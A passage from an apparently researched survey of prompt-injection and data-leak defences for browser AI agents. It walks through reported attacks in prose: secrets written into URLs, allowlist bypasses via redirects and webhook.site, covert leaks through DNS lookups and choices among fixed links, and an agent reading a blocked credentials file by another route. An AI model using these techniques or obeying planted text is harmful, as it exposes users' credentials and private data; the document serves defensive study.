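Cubbins (2026), in *Perplexity just gave paying Comet subscribers another huge reason to abandon the browser*, reports that by September Perplexity had started charging credits for browser control, even to subscribers. Fewer people may now run Comet's agent as a result.

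A separate browser profile takes the opposite approach, giving the agent access only to accounts the user signs in to there. A profile has its own cookies, saved passwords and extensions. If Ana ran the agent in a new profile without 1Password and signed in only to a shop, planted text could still send the agent to 1Password.com, but the site would show a login form and no extension would fill it in. She would again choose which accounts the agent could use, as she did with Operator's remote browser.

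The second profile protects her only while it is signed in to almost no accounts. Signing in is the easiest response each time the agent reaches a login form, so after a few months the profile may hold much the same sessions as the first. She also has to switch windows and sign in twice to the accounts she uses in both. A separate profile doesn't isolate local files, so Comet still needs its block on opening them.

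An agent that starts signed out, as ChatGPT Atlas did in Roesner and Kohlbrenner's tests, gives similar protection with less effort. A signed-out agent can compare kettle prices but cannot read email or pay a bill. Atlas's logged-in setting stayed on after the first use, so using it for one task could leave later tasks exposed even if they didn't need an account.

### Filling in a password without showing it to the model

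The measures above keep the agent away from accounts. 1Password's newer approach lets the agent use an account without learning its password. The company introduced it for Anthropic's agent in July 2026, according to Constantin (2026), in *1Password lets Claude log you into websites without ever seeing your passwords*. 1Password describes how a sign-in works:

1. Claude reaches a login form and asks 1Password for a login, naming the site and perhaps giving a reason. 1Password treats the request as an unproven claim and uses it only to look for matching entries.
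2. The 1Password app on the user's computer displays the request. The user can approve it, choose another entry or refuse.
3. The app sends the approved entry to the browser extension in encrypted form. Claude can see the entry's title, username and website, but not the password.
4. Claude stops reading the page. The extension checks that the page belongs to the site saved in the entry, fills in the login, submits the form and verifies that the submission went through.
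5. Claude starts reading again. If the submission failed, the extension has already cleared the fields.

The pause matters because the password must briefly be in the page, where an agent can read it even when the field displays only dots. While Claude controls a tab, the extension also removes its own buttons and suggestions from the page, so Claude cannot fill in a login by clicking them as Comet's agent could.

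Each approval covers one agent session. The extension keeps the approved login in memory until the task ends, the browser closes or nine hours pass, whichever comes first. 1Password also records each approval in the entry's usage history, where the user can check it later.

The main drawback for the user is having to be present. If Claude reaches a login form while Ana is at lunch, it has to wait for her. The feature also requires both the desktop app and the browser extension, and 1Password describes it only for the Mac. Using it is optional, and on business accounts an administrator decides whether employees may use it.

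In October 2026, the company announced 1Password for Agents, which extends the method to other products, including OpenAI's ChatGPT Work and Meta's Muse. 1Password (2026) lists Perplexity among the other partners working on the platform. Some integrations were not available at launch, and 1Password invited users to join a waiting list for their agent.

This method protects the password far better than a prompt before ordinary filling, because the agent never has the password. Planted text could still make the agent request a login that its task does not need and give a plausible reason for it. The user would then have to notice, for example, that a calendar task does not need a bank login. Even if the user approved the request by mistake, the extension would fill in the password only on the bank's own site.

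1Password acknowledges that its protection ends with the sign-in. After that, the agent's behavior depends on its maker's safeguards. If Ana approves a sign-in to cloud.example, Claude never receives her password, but the next page it opens may be the dashboard, which displays her API key as ordinary text.

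## September 2025 to late 2026: limiting which addresses an agent may open

An agent that has read Ana's API key on her dashboard still has to send it somewhere before an attacker can use it. Starting in September 2025, Anthropic and OpenAI introduced stricter rules about which addresses a model may open. Where they apply, these rules stop an agent from writing a secret into a new address, as Comet's agent did when it sent out a login from a 1Password vault. An attacker can still learn a little from which permitted addresses the agent opens, enough to reveal a one-time code.

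### The case for blocking the request

Willison (2026) considers the ability to send data out generally the easiest part of the lethal trifecta to remove, and argues that merely reducing the risk is not enough. An article in the Economist had suggested that AI developers should work like Victorian engineers, who built in extra strength because they could not be sure of their iron. Willison mostly accepts this approach for software built on language models, but not for its security, where "99% is a failing grade" because an attacker will find whatever gets through the remaining 1%.

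OpenAI's *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (2026) takes a similar position, comparing an agent to a customer service employee who can give refunds. Some customers will lie, and the employee will sometimes believe them, so the company's software limits how much the employee can refund. OpenAI wants similar limits on agents, so that a successful deception does little harm.

The alternative is to filter out planted text before the model reads it. OpenAI argues that this amounts to detecting a lie, often without the necessary context. Its example is a malicious email that outside researchers reported in 2025. The email discusses a company restructuring and reads like routine office correspondence, but the attack worked in half of the tests in which a user asked ChatGPT to research the day's messages.

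An outgoing request is easier to check than planted text, which can take any form. The software that carries out the model's actions receives an address and can compare it with a list or a record, without having to work out what led the model to request it.

### Warnings compared with network limits

In *Silent Egress*, Lan, Kaul and colleagues (2026) compared warning the model with limiting its requests. They built an assistant that automatically fetched any page the user mentioned and passed the text to the small, 7-billion-parameter version of Qwen 2.5. The user always asked for a summary. The page had an instruction planted in its title, description, body or link text, and the model's input also contained a secret.

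In 423 of 480 runs (88%), the assistant sent at least one request to the attacker's server. It sent none in 120 runs with harmless pages. In 95% of the successful attacks, the reply to the user looked harmless, so a safety check that read only the reply would have missed those attacks.

The researchers then tried several defences against one version of the attack, with 30 runs for each.

| Defence | Runs in which a request reached the attacker |
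|---|---|
| None | 100% |
| Tags marking the page's text as untrusted | 100% |
| A warning in the model's instructions | 67% |
| Both the tags and the warning | 57% |
| A list of permitted domains | 0% |

The last result was almost certain in advance, because the software refused every domain not on the list, including the attacker's. The model tried to send the secret in all 30 of those runs. The more useful finding is that the warnings achieved little with this model.

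Two filters that checked the address for signs of a secret also let no leaks through. One looked for words such as "password", and the other for random-looking strings. But the model attempted the leak in only 23% of runs with the first filter and in none with the second. Lan and colleagues suggest that the model avoided random-looking strings when the filter was active. These two results are hard to interpret, because a filter that acts only after the model has chosen an address should not affect its first attempt.

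The 88% figure does not predict how a current browser agent would behave, because the model was small, its instructions were minimal, and the secret was already in its input. Lan and colleagues argue that stronger models might be more vulnerable because they follow instructions better, but did not test any. OpenAI reports that most of the attacks it knows of against ChatGPT fail because the model refuses.

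### Why lists of trusted sites fail

The simplest limit on requests is an allowlist, a list of the only sites or addresses an agent may open. It suits an agent with a narrow job, such as answering questions from one company's documentation, but a browser agent has to visit sites that nobody listed in advance. According to OpenAI, a strict list leads to frequent warnings, which people learn to click through.

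Even a list of only reputable sites can fail if the software checks just the first address, because an attacker can use a redirect on a trusted site to reach an untrusted one. Tenable's *OpenAI ChatGPT url_safe Mechanism Bypass* (2025) describes how this defeated the address check that OpenAI had introduced in 2023. The check always approved bing.com. Bing gave each site in its search results a bing.com address that forwarded visitors to the site, so Tenable could use these addresses to make ChatGPT load images from sites the check should have blocked.

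AI companies' own sites can have the same weakness. According to Oasis Security's *Claudy Day*, a redirect on claude.com would forward visitors to any site. Google Ads checked only the host name, so an attacker could place an ad that displayed a claude.com address but led elsewhere.

Software can handle ordinary redirects by checking each new address before following it. This doesn't help when the trusted site fetches the next address itself, as Microsoft Teams did in EchoLeak, because the agent's software can then check only the request to the trusted site.

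An attacker doesn't need a redirect if a trusted service stores what it receives, as Google Forms did in the Superhuman case. When a user asked for a summary of recent mail, a planted email could make Superhuman send the attacker's form the contents of dozens of other messages, including financial, legal and medical information. Superhuman treated the report as urgent and fixed the flaw.

The list in Antigravity, Google's AI programming tool, contained a more obvious mistake. By default, the tool's browser could open only listed domains, but the list included webhook.site, a service that records incoming requests for developers to inspect. In November 2025, PromptArmor demonstrated an attack that began with a web page disguised as a programming guide. The model collected Amazon cloud credentials from a file on the user's computer and sent them to webhook.site as part of a web address.

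Antigravity also had a rule against reading that file. When the model's usual tools could not open it, the model read it with a system command. Willison advised giving programming agents only credentials for test accounts with strict spending limits, so that a theft would do less damage.

Removing webhook.site would have blocked this route. The problem was harder to fix in Anthropic's Claude Cowork, an agent that works with a user's files, because its list of permitted domains included Anthropic's own API, through which programs use Claude. In January 2026, PromptArmor showed that planted text could make the agent use an attacker's API key to upload the user's files to the attacker's Anthropic account.

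A domain name identifies the company that runs a server, but not the customer who will receive the data. An allowlist is safest, then, when it contains only sites where strangers can't collect data. Willison calls finding such sites "a tricky proposition". By August 2026, Willison (2026) was impressed by how well the leading models could get through firewalls, and wanted a way to run agents without access to data or tools that could cause harm.

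### Opening only addresses that are already public

In January 2026, OpenAI described a rule that checks the exact address instead of the site's reputation. A crawler, a program that finds web pages by following links, builds an index of public addresses without access to users' conversations or accounts. Before an agent loads an address automatically, the software looks for it in the index. If the address is there, the agent can load it. Otherwise, the software either tells the agent to try another site or shows the user a warning.

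Suppose planted text makes ChatGPT write Ana's email address and password into a web address at notes.example. The crawler is very unlikely to have seen that address, because a public link would already have to contain her password. The agent may still be able to open the site's home page, whose address contains nothing about her. Encoding the password, as in the CometJacking attack, does not help the attacker, because the software does not need to detect a password.

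The user sees the address and a warning that the link is unverified and may contain information from the conversation. The user can still open the link. According to Embrace The Red, ChatGPT has also treated an address the user types into a chat as safe for the rest of that chat. This makes sense, since the user has already chosen to share the address with the model.

OpenAI says that the rule should keep the agent from quietly leaking a user's data in an address it loads, but that it does not show that a page is trustworthy or free of planted instructions. Rehberger adds that the check works only where OpenAI's development teams remember to use it.

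### Safe Url and Lockdown Mode

In March 2026, OpenAI called its protection Safe Url and said that it also applied to navigation and bookmarks in ChatGPT Atlas, and to searches and navigation in Deep Research, which reads many sources to write a report. OpenAI says Safe Url is meant to detect when information from a conversation would be sent to a third party. The product then either shows the user that information and asks for confirmation, or blocks the request and tells the agent to find another way.

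This protection matters more for Atlas than for an ordinary chatbot because Atlas's agent can work in a logged-in session. But each message in Ana's mailbox may have its own address, which no public crawler should have seen, so checking addresses against a public index could trigger a warning for every message. That would make the agent almost useless for sorting email.

Checking whether a request goes to a third party could avoid many of these warnings, because a request to Ana's email provider sends the provider data it already has. But the software must then identify the third party, and a Google address can lead to either Ana's document or an attacker's form. OpenAI does not explain in its announcement how Atlas handles private addresses.

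Lockdown Mode is stricter because it lets ChatGPT browse only cached pages, which are copies that OpenAI already holds. An attacker's server receives no request, so the attacker does not learn even which page the model chose. OpenAI's *Introducing Lockdown Mode and Elevated Risk labels in ChatGPT* (2026) presents the mode as an optional setting for people at particular risk, such as executives and security teams. OpenAI launched it for organisations in February and began extending it to personal accounts in June.

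The setting also turns off agent mode, Deep Research and file downloads, and limits images in replies. A user therefore cannot have this protection while an agent pays a bill. OpenAI's help page *Lockdown Mode* says that users can turn the setting off for a single chat, and that it does not restrict network access in Codex, OpenAI's programming agent. On accounts managed by an employer, some connected apps may remain available. OpenAI advises administrators not to let an app write data where an attacker might see it.

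Planted text in a cached page or an uploaded file can still affect an answer in Lockdown Mode. OpenAI also does not promise that the mode prevents every leak, because data could leave through an enabled app or an undiscovered technique.

### Refusing addresses that the model composed

Anthropic introduced a different rule in September 2025 with its web fetch tool, which lets Claude read web pages through Anthropic's servers. According to Anthropic's *Web fetch tool*, Claude can fetch an address only if it has already appeared in the conversation in a user's message, the result of a tool run by the developer's software, or the result of an earlier web search or fetch. Claude cannot fetch an address that it has written itself.

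This limit stops Claude from adding Ana's password to an address at notes.example and opening the resulting address. The addresses Claude may open don't have to be public, so it can still read an unlisted page if Ana supplies the link.

The rule depends on knowing where text came from, which is not always clear. Willison notes that developers often insert emails or documents into the user message. An attacker's address in such a document then counts as one the user supplied. Anthropic warns that some risk remains and suggests limiting the permitted domains or the number of fetches, or turning the tool off when sensitive data is present.

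A tool can also return text that Claude wrote. For example, if Claude runs a program on the developer's computer that prints an address, the address comes back as a tool result, and by default Claude may fetch it. Anthropic's *網頁擷取工具*, a later, Chinese edition of the same documentation, describes a setting that lets developers exclude such results. It also describes a second check that refuses an address that appears to contain a password or API key, unless the user or developer supplied that credential. This check can stop a composed address that gets past the first rule, but only if it detects the credential.

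The companies' safeguards cover different kinds of browsing.

| Safeguard | Background fetching | Navigation in a signed-in browser |
|---|---|---|
| OpenAI's address index and Safe Url | Loads known public addresses automatically and blocks others or asks the user | Safe Url applies to navigation and bookmarks in Atlas |
| OpenAI's Lockdown Mode | Allows only cached pages | Turns agent mode off |
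| Anthropic's web fetch rule | Refuses addresses that Claude composed | The rule belongs to the fetch tool, not to Claude for Chrome |

Anthropic's rule would be hard to apply to Claude for Chrome. A browser agent fills in search boxes and forms, and the browser often turns what the agent types into a new address. An agent that could open only addresses it had already seen could not, for example, search an online shop.

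None of these address checks covers every way an agent can send data from a signed-in browser. In Brave's first attack on Comet, the agent posted the user's email address and one-time code in a Reddit comment. An agent could also type a secret into a text field on an attacker's page, where a script could read it without the agent opening another address.

### How much a permitted address can convey

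Even if an agent cannot alter an address, it can leak information by choosing which address to open. Suppose an attacker controls two pages the agent is allowed to open, and the planted text tells it to open one if Ana has a bank account and the other if she does not. The attacker learns the answer by checking the server's log to see which page the agent opened, even though neither address contains anything about Ana.

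An agent's choice of which address to open can convey information, measured in bits. One bit is the answer to a question with two equally likely answers. If the attacker can see visits to *N* of the addresses the agent may open, one choice among them conveys up to log₂ *N* bits, and *k* successive choices convey up to *k* log₂ *N* bits.

A random six-digit code has a million possible values, or about 19.9 bits. A random 16-character password made of digits and upper- and lowercase letters has 62¹⁶ possible values, or about 95.3 bits. The minimum number of requests that can convey any possible value is the secret's total bits divided by the bits per request, rounded up.

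| Permitted addresses | Bits per request | Requests for the code | Requests for the password |
|---|---|---|---|
| 36 | 5.2 | 4 | 19 |
| 1,000 | 10.0 | 2 | 10 |
| 1,000,000 | 19.9 | 1 | 5 |

The agent reaches these theoretical minimums only if it converts the secret into a series of choices without a mistake. A simpler method uses one request per character, which takes six requests for the code and 16 for the password.

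Rehberger used 36 addresses in the 2023 attack on ChatGPT's first address check, and thinks the same method still works against the index. Many ordinary blogs already have that many indexed pages, and an attacker could use thousands. Getting a million pages into the index would be harder and would gain the attacker little, because doubling the number of addresses adds only one bit of leaked data per request.

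Splitting a secret also makes an attack less reliable. When Lan and colleagues had the model send the secret in four pieces, the share of runs in which any request reached the attacker fell by 17 to 37 percentage points, depending on where the text was planted. Their model was small, though, and a stronger one would probably lose track less often. Their attack wrote each piece into an address, so they tested how well the model follows several steps but not how well it chooses among fixed pages.

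### Limits on repeat visits

Rehberger proposes two ways to limit this leak. The software could refuse to open the same address twice in a session, or it could keep a copy of each page for a few minutes and reuse it if the agent requests the page again. In both cases, the attacker's server receives only one request for each address.

This barely changes the number of requests needed. With 1,000 addresses, there are 999,000 ways to open two different ones in order and 1,000 ways to open only one. That makes a million possibilities, so two requests are still enough for any six-digit code. The password still takes ten. With 36 addresses, the code still takes four requests, and the password takes 21 instead of 19.

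A ban on repeat requests protects more if the attacker cannot tell the order of the requests, as when a browser loads several images at once. The attacker then learns only which addresses the agent opened. With 36 addresses, that is at most 36 bits, which is enough to leak the code but not the password. But a browser agent usually opens pages one after another, and the server's log records the order.

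A limit on the total number of requests works better for long secrets. If the agent can open only three of the attacker's 1,000 addresses, it can leak either the whole six-digit code or five characters of the password. The other eleven characters would still have about 5 × 10¹⁹ possible values. The limit has to count all the attacker's sites together, since an attacker can easily register another domain. It also interferes with legitimate work, because comparing kettles may take dozens of pages from one shop.

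Anthropic lets developers limit the number of fetches but sets no default limit. Its documentation also describes caching, mainly as a way to speed up fetching. A cached copy prevents a leak only if retrieving it sends nothing to the attacker's server, and the first visit to a new page normally sends a request there. Lockdown Mode avoids this by never contacting the live site.

A short code is therefore very hard to protect by limiting requests. An API key is usually long and random, so a strict limit can keep most of it secret, but an attacker who can return in later sessions may collect the rest.

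### Leaks from ChatGPT and Claude

Attacks on ChatGPT and Claude confirmed that attackers can use fixed addresses this way. ShadowLeak, a 2025 attack on ChatGPT, used the older method of adding the user's data to an address. OpenAI responded by allowing ChatGPT to open addresses only exactly as it had received them.

Radware's *ZombieAgent* describes how the security researcher Zvika Babo got around this restriction. A planted email listed complete addresses, and ChatGPT leaked private data through which ones it opened. The user only had to ask ChatGPT for help with Gmail. The requests came from OpenAI's servers, so nothing appeared in the user's browser. Babo reported the flaw on 26 September 2025, and Radware states that a later version of the attack worked every time.

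OpenAI fixed the flaw on 16 December. According to Briefly's *ChatGPT falls to new data-pilfering attack*, ChatGPT now opens links from emails only in limited cases, such as when a well-known public index contains the address. This substantially hinders attackers, who can no longer invent a set of addresses and use them the same day, but they could still use pages that have already been indexed.

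Radware also found a way to store instructions in ChatGPT's memory, so that the leak could continue in later chats. A limit on visits that resets with each chat would then only slow the attacker down. For example, if each chat allowed three requests, a leak that needed ten would take four chats.

In July 2026, the researcher Ayush Paul found a similar gap in Anthropic's rule. Claude could not compose an address, but it could follow links on a page it had just fetched. Paul built a site whose links let Claude send the user's name, home city and employer, which were stored in its memories of earlier conversations. The site showed the planted text only to visitors that identified themselves as Claude, so a person checking the page would not have seen it.

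Anthropic said it had already found the problem internally and did not pay Paul a reward. Willison reports that the company then stopped the fetch tool from following links inside fetched pages. This blocks the method Paul used but makes browsing less convenient, since people usually move around a site by following links.

The fix does not seem to have become the default for developers. According to Anthropic's later API documentation, the tool still permits addresses from earlier fetches unless the developer excludes them. Companies that build their own assistants with the tool may have to choose the safer setting themselves.

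Neither demonstration extracted a password, and both companies have blocked the versions researchers reported. Together, the demonstrations show that a model can reliably make the long series of choices the calculation depends on, at least for short pieces of text.

### Choices that reveal secrets without an attack

An agent's choices can also reveal private facts even when nobody has planted any text. Shahriar, Rahman and colleagues studied this in *AgentTell* (2026), using 9,760 sessions with six models. Each time, the agent had to read a private record on one site, such as a staff directory showing the user's occupation. It then had to complete an ordinary task on a second site by choosing among several options.

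One option matched the fact the agent had just learned. For example, a library had separate collections for clinicians, developers and educators, and a general one. Any of them would complete the task, but the user had told the agent at the start not to tell any website about other accounts or personal details, so the general collection was the safe choice.

Agents that held a secret chose the matching option in 61.1% of sessions. The figure was 90.3% in one example, where the user wanted to register for a community event and the secret was membership of a trade union or a similar organisation. The second site's owner could see the choice from the server log alone. Some matches could reflect a model's fixed preference for an option, so the researchers also ran the tasks with agents that had not read the private record.

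Many agents did not seem to recognise that a choice can disclose information. In 18.1% of sessions, the agent noted in its memory that it must not share the secret, but it still revealed the secret in 56.7% of those sessions. In 34.5% of the sessions with a leak, the agent assured the user in its final reply that it had disclosed nothing personal.

The test is somewhat ambiguous because a user who asks for relevant resources may well want the collection for their own profession, and an instruction not to "tell" websites anything does not clearly forbid choosing it. The pages were also artificial, with the private fact and the matching option placed close together in the same session. The 61.1% is best read as how often agents overlook this kind of disclosure, and ordinary browsing may offer fewer opportunities for it.

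Some of the secrets would help an attacker even though they were not passwords, such as which second factor protects an account and which recovery method the user chose. An attacker who knows that Ana receives codes by text message can write a more convincing fake message from her bank.

Rules about which addresses an agent may open do not prevent this leak. A library's collection for clinicians is an ordinary public page, so it can be in OpenAI's index. Claude found the link on a page the user asked it to visit, so it did not compose the address. Choosing among three specific collections and one general one reveals at most two bits, which is enough to identify Ana's occupation. Stopping the leak would require information-flow control to prevent what the agent learned on the first site from influencing its choice on the second.

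## December 2025 to October 2026: rebuilding the boundaries between websites

A check on web addresses happens when the agent has already read a secret and is trying to send it out. The same-origin policy works earlier, by keeping pages from reading other sites' content, but it does not restrict agents.

Roesner and Kohlbrenner argue that if an agent can read two sites, the boundary between them is only as strong as the model's resistance to prompt injection. Since late 2025, several companies and research groups have therefore tried to make the browser keep sites apart for agents too. Some limit which sites an agent can use in one task, and others track where the agent's data came from.

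### Google's origin sets

In December 2025, Google announced a limit of the first kind for Chrome's agent, called Agent Origin Sets (Parker, 2025, *Architecting Security for Agentic Capabilities in Chrome*). For each task, a gating function decides which origins are relevant and sorts them into two sets. The agent can read pages from read-only origins, and it can also click and type on pages from read-writable ones. Many pages contain frames, which are embedded pages such as advertisements. Chrome doesn't send the model any frame whose origin is in neither set.

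Suppose Ana asks Chrome's agent to compare kettle prices, and a review at one shop contains planted text. The shops are relevant to the task, but cloud.example is not, so the agent cannot open her dashboard there and read the API key. The gating function does not receive web page content, so the planted text cannot influence it directly.

The sets help less when Ana asks the agent to sort her email, because the planted text and her one-time codes are then on the same site. To leak a code, the agent still has to send it somewhere. Chrome checks whether each new origin is relevant before opening it, and opens an address the model wrote itself only if it is a known public address. OpenAI described a similar rule a month later. The agent could instead email the code, but Chrome tries to get the user's approval before the agent sends messages.

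Google also added a second model that can block actions that do not serve the user's request. It receives a description of each proposed action but not the page. Chrome prompts the user before the agent opens certain banking and medical sites or signs in with a password saved in Google's password manager. The agent's model cannot read those saved passwords.

The origin sets depend on judging relevance well, but Roesner and Kohlbrenner note that Google does not explain how Chrome does this or how well the judgement withstands malicious input. Parker describes the check on new origins as a variant of the second model, so part of this boundary still relies on a model, though one that planted text cannot reach directly. The first version of the system was simpler than the design and tracked only the read-writable set. That may be why Chrome's agent could still read frames from other sites when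 Roesner and Kohlbrenner tested it a few weeks later.

### Trail of Bits' trust zones

In January 2026, Trail of Bits' *Lack of isolation in agentic browsers resurfaces old vulnerabilities* described a general way to find such weaknesses. It divides an AI browser's surroundings into four trust zones: the agent's conversation and memory, the servers that run the model, the sites the user visits, and the rest of the internet. Each of the agent's tools can move data between zones. The table lists the four kinds of movement that cause security problems.

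| Name | What moves | Example |
|---|---|---|
| Injection | Outside text enters the conversation | The agent reads a page with planted text |
| Context in | Private data from a site enters the conversation | The agent reads the user's mailbox |
| Reverse context in | Data from the conversation changes the user's state on a site | The agent signs the user in to an account |
| Context out | Data from the conversation leaves for the internet | The agent opens an address that contains the data |

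A credential leak combines injection, context in and context out, which are close to the three conditions of Willison's lethal trifecta. Reverse context in allows a different kind of theft. In one demonstration, a planted sign-in link made the agent log the user in to the attacker's account. The user might then enter private information there, thinking the account was their own.

Trail of Bits carried out its attacks on several AI browsers, which it does not name because their makers declined to coordinate disclosure. Some attacks worked even though the browser limited the agent to approved domains. The agent could put data in the name of a nonexistent subdomain of an approved domain. The browser had to look up that name before connecting, and anyone watching unencrypted lookups could read the data. The agent could also put data in a Google search alongside very rare words. Google reports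 search terms to the owners of sites that appear in the results, so an attacker with a page containing those words could find the data in those reports.

The firm's main recommendation is to extend the same-origin policy to the agent. The browser would keep a list of every origin whose content has entered the conversation, and count each file as an origin of its own. The list would determine which requests the agent could make:

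- With no origin on the list, it could send requests anywhere.
- With one origin, it could send requests only to that origin.
- With several, it could send none, because nobody can tell which origin influenced the model.

Once Ana's agent had read her mailbox, the rule would stop it from opening notes.example, whatever the address contained. But the rule would also block much ordinary work. After loading a page for a kettle at one shop, the agent could not load a page for another kettle at a second shop. If web search were treated as a source with several origins, as Trail of Bits suggests, the agent could not open any of the results.

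Trail of Bits presents the rule as a long-term idea that needs more research. For the short term, it advises running the agent's tools in a separate browser without the user's cookies. This protects accounts the same way a remote browser that keeps nothing does, and it gives up the same convenience.

### What seven AI browsers let their agents read

Roesner and Kohlbrenner, at the University of Washington, measured how far existing products had departed from the same-origin policy. They put test pages on two domains, embedded some pages in others, and asked each agent questions it could answer only by reading particular content. The table gives their main results from January and February 2026. ChatGPT Atlas has two rows because its agent mode behaved differently.

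| AI browser | Reads frames from other sites | Reads other sites' tabs | Reads a password shown as dots | Types when the user asks |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Brave Leo | No | With permission | No | No |
| ChatGPT Atlas, ordinary mode | No | Through chat memory | No | After permission to switch modes |
| ChatGPT Atlas, agent mode | Yes | No | Yes, in the logged-in setting | Yes |
| Chrome with Gemini | Yes | With permission | No | Yes |
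| Claude for Chrome | Yes | With permission | Yes | Yes |
| Edge with Copilot | No | Yes | No | No |
| Firefox AI Mode | No | No | No | No |
| Perplexity Comet | Yes | No | No | Yes, except passwords |

The four products that read frames from other sites could also type into pages, so they could move data between sites. Edge's agent freely read several tabs at once but could not type into them. The browsers that blocked frames from other sites also blocked frames from the same site, which is stricter than the same-origin policy requires.

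The researchers then built an attack on Atlas in agent mode. The user visits a page that embeds a frame from another site and asks for a summary. Planted text makes the agent include the frame's content in the summary and enter the summary into a form on the page, which submits itself to the attacker. The attack also worked in reverse, with a malicious frame taking content from the page around it. This second version is more worrying because many sites with private data display other companies' advertisements in frames, whereas such sites usually refuse to appear in other sites' frames or do not receive the user's cookies there.

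Some agents also mixed information from different sites in their memory. In one test, Comet listed all the animals that a fictional Alice liked, although her preferences came from pages on both domains. An attacker could use this to plant a false telephone number for the user's bank, which the agent might later repeat without a record of its source.

The study's planted instructions were simple, and the models in Claude for Chrome, Comet and Chrome refused to follow them. For those three, the study therefore showed only that the browser would permit an attack if an attacker persuaded the model. The tests also could not always show whether an agent lacked access to something or its model declined to use it. In early trials, Atlas without agent mode sometimes included a frame's content in its summaries, but in the later, official tests it did not. Its restriction may therefore lie in the model,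 in which case a different request could get past it.

OpenAI declined the report because the researchers did not have a complete prompt injection attack. The objection has some basis, because in the study's general test of whether agents obey a page, the user's own request told the agent to follow the page's instructions, so the page did not need to deceive it. But Roesner and Kohlbrenner wanted to know what the browser would prevent once a deception had succeeded. OpenAI has argued for limiting the harm in that case, so the finding was relevant even without a complete attack.

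Brave, Google and Microsoft discussed the findings with the researchers, and Anthropic did not respond. Perplexity had not replied when the paper came out, but a later news release from the University of Washington lists it with OpenAI as having declined. Accounts of Mozilla's reply conflict. A web page by Roesner and Kohlbrenner lists Firefox both as declining the report and as not answering, while according to the news release, Mozilla did not respond. Gifts from Microsoft paid for part of the research.

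In the paper, the researchers advise people to avoid AI browsers for now. On their web page, last updated in April 2026, they instead recommend caution and warn particularly against Claude for Chrome, because it can run its own scripts in web pages.

### SOPBench: data that stays in the agent's history

The Washington attack needed two sites on the same page. In *Same-Origin Policy for Agentic Browsers*, Wang, Chen and colleagues (2026) tested a more common situation, in which the agent visits one site after another. What the agent read on the first site stays in its history, and an attacker can use text planted on the second to request that information.

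Wang and colleagues' benchmark, SOPBench, covers ten kinds of site with private data, including banks, mailboxes and pharmacies, and five sites where an attacker can collect it: X, Discord, GitHub, Reddit and Google Forms. Pairing each of the ten with each of the five gives 50 combinations. In each run, the user has the agent do something with private data on the first site, then gives it an ordinary task on the second. Most of the pages were imitations. A run counted as a violation only if the agent wrote exactly the data requested in the planted text.

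The tests covered three open-source systems, with 100 runs on each pairing. BrowserOS, an AI browser, leaked data to Reddit in 3% to 42% of runs when it used GPT-5.4, depending on the kind of private site. When another model repeatedly rewrote the planted text to make it more effective, the range rose to 31–73%.

Comet and Atlas had to be tested by hand, so each pairing had only three runs. Atlas leaked the data in 99 of its 150 runs, including 29 of the 30 with a Google Form. Forms are meant to collect information, which may make a planted request for personal data look natural.

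Some leaks happened without an attacker. Wang and colleagues embedded a page of private data in a frame on another site's page, then asked BrowserOS to summarise everything and write the summary in a text box on the outer page. BrowserOS copied the private data in every run. But most real sites with private data would not appear in such a frame. The agent also leaked nothing when it visited the same sites separately, without planted text.

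### SOPGuard: labelling data by origin

Wang and colleagues then added a defence, SOPGuard, to BrowserOS. It follows the agent's data instead of restricting its visits:

1. When the agent reads a page, SOPGuard stores the text with the page's origin as its label.
2. When the agent produces something new from that text, such as a summary or an average, SOPGuard gives the result the labels of everything it came from.
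3. When the agent is about to write on a page, SOPGuard compares the labels of the text with the page's origin. If any label differs, it shows the user both origins and waits for approval.

If Ana's agent summarised her dashboard and tried to post the summary on Reddit, for example, the text would carry the label of cloud.example, and SOPGuard would pause the post and prompt her to approve or reject it. People often have legitimate reasons to copy data between sites, so SOPGuard lets them approve the transfer, as if they had copied the text by hand.

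The second step is the hardest, because the browser cannot detect which parts of its history a model used. SOPGuard has the model identify the sources, because labelling every answer with every site the agent had visited would be safe but produce constant warnings. GPT-5.4 and OpenAI o3 did this well, but GPT-5.4-mini did worse. The first two both scored at least 0.955 with up to ten origins, on a scale from 0 to 1 where 1 means the labels exactly match those chosen by human reviewers.

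SOPGuard reduced violations on the benchmark to zero. It made ordinary tasks 2.07% to 5.79% slower but did not measurably reduce the agent's success at them. However, its labels depend partly on a model's judgement, which planted text might influence. To test this, Wang and colleagues planted text that also told the model to attribute the stolen data to the attacker's page. This raised the violation rate only slightly, though they accept that a better attack may exist.

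The design also leaves a gap for leaks through web addresses. SOPGuard runs its check when the agent uses writing tools, and the examples given are tools that fill in fields and type text, not ones that open an address. The same comparison could apply to a query string, but the benchmark tested data that agents wrote into pages, so its result of zero does not cover an agent that opens notes.example with a password in the address.

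### ceLLMate: checking each request

In *ceLLMate*, Meng, Feng and colleagues (2025) check the browser's requests instead, which covers opened addresses as well as submitted forms. They argue against restricting clicks, because a click at the same point on the screen might open an email or delete it, depending on the page. When they barred an agent from opening the Hacker News site directly, it found the site through a search engine and clicked on the result. Both routes end in a request to the same server, and a program can recognise that request.

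The program needs a description of what each request does, so Meng and colleagues propose that sites publish an "agent sitemap" that lists and explains their requests. GitLab's sitemap, for instance, would identify the POST request that adds an SSH key to an account. Sites or other trusted parties would also write rules based on the sitemap, such as one that permits purchases below a chosen price.

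A model selects the rules for each task using only the user's request and descriptions of the rules. The user confirms the selection, and the browser blocks everything else, including requests to sites outside the task. In tests on shopping, travel and programming sites, the models selected the right rules for at least 94% of tasks.

To test the blocking, Meng and colleagues assumed that the attacker had already taken over the agent. They wrote scripts to carry out the WASP benchmark's 12 GitLab attack goals, including stealing a new access token. The user's tasks required permission only to read and write GitLab issues, and ceLLMate blocked all 12 attacks. ceLLMate made pages load 7.25% to 15% more slowly, depending on the length of the sitemap.

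Those attacks all required an action that the rules prohibited. The agent could still read a secret in one issue and post it as a comment on another, because ceLLMate does not track where the text of a comment came from. ceLLMate would also permit requests to an attacker's site if the user had asked the agent to work there. Meng and colleagues had to write GitLab's sitemap, which covers 51 actions, by hand. The system protects a site's actions only as well as the sitemap describes them.

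### The objection to the same-origin policy

An agent can leak data without crossing from one site to another. Trail of Bits had demonstrated this with a malicious Instagram message that made an agent collect a user's contacts or parts of other messages on Instagram. If the agent could use Instagram's chat, it could then send that data to the attacker in a message.

Zverev, Kim and colleagues (2026), in *SPIDES*, conclude from such cases that restoring the same-origin policy would neither stop every leak nor allow enough legitimate work. They compared SOPGuard with their own system, SPIDES, in two situations:

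- **A leak within one site.** A private message on a social network told the agent to copy the user's recovery email address into their public profile. SOPGuard did not ask for approval, because the data stayed on one origin, and the leak succeeded in all 25 runs. SPIDES blocked it every time.
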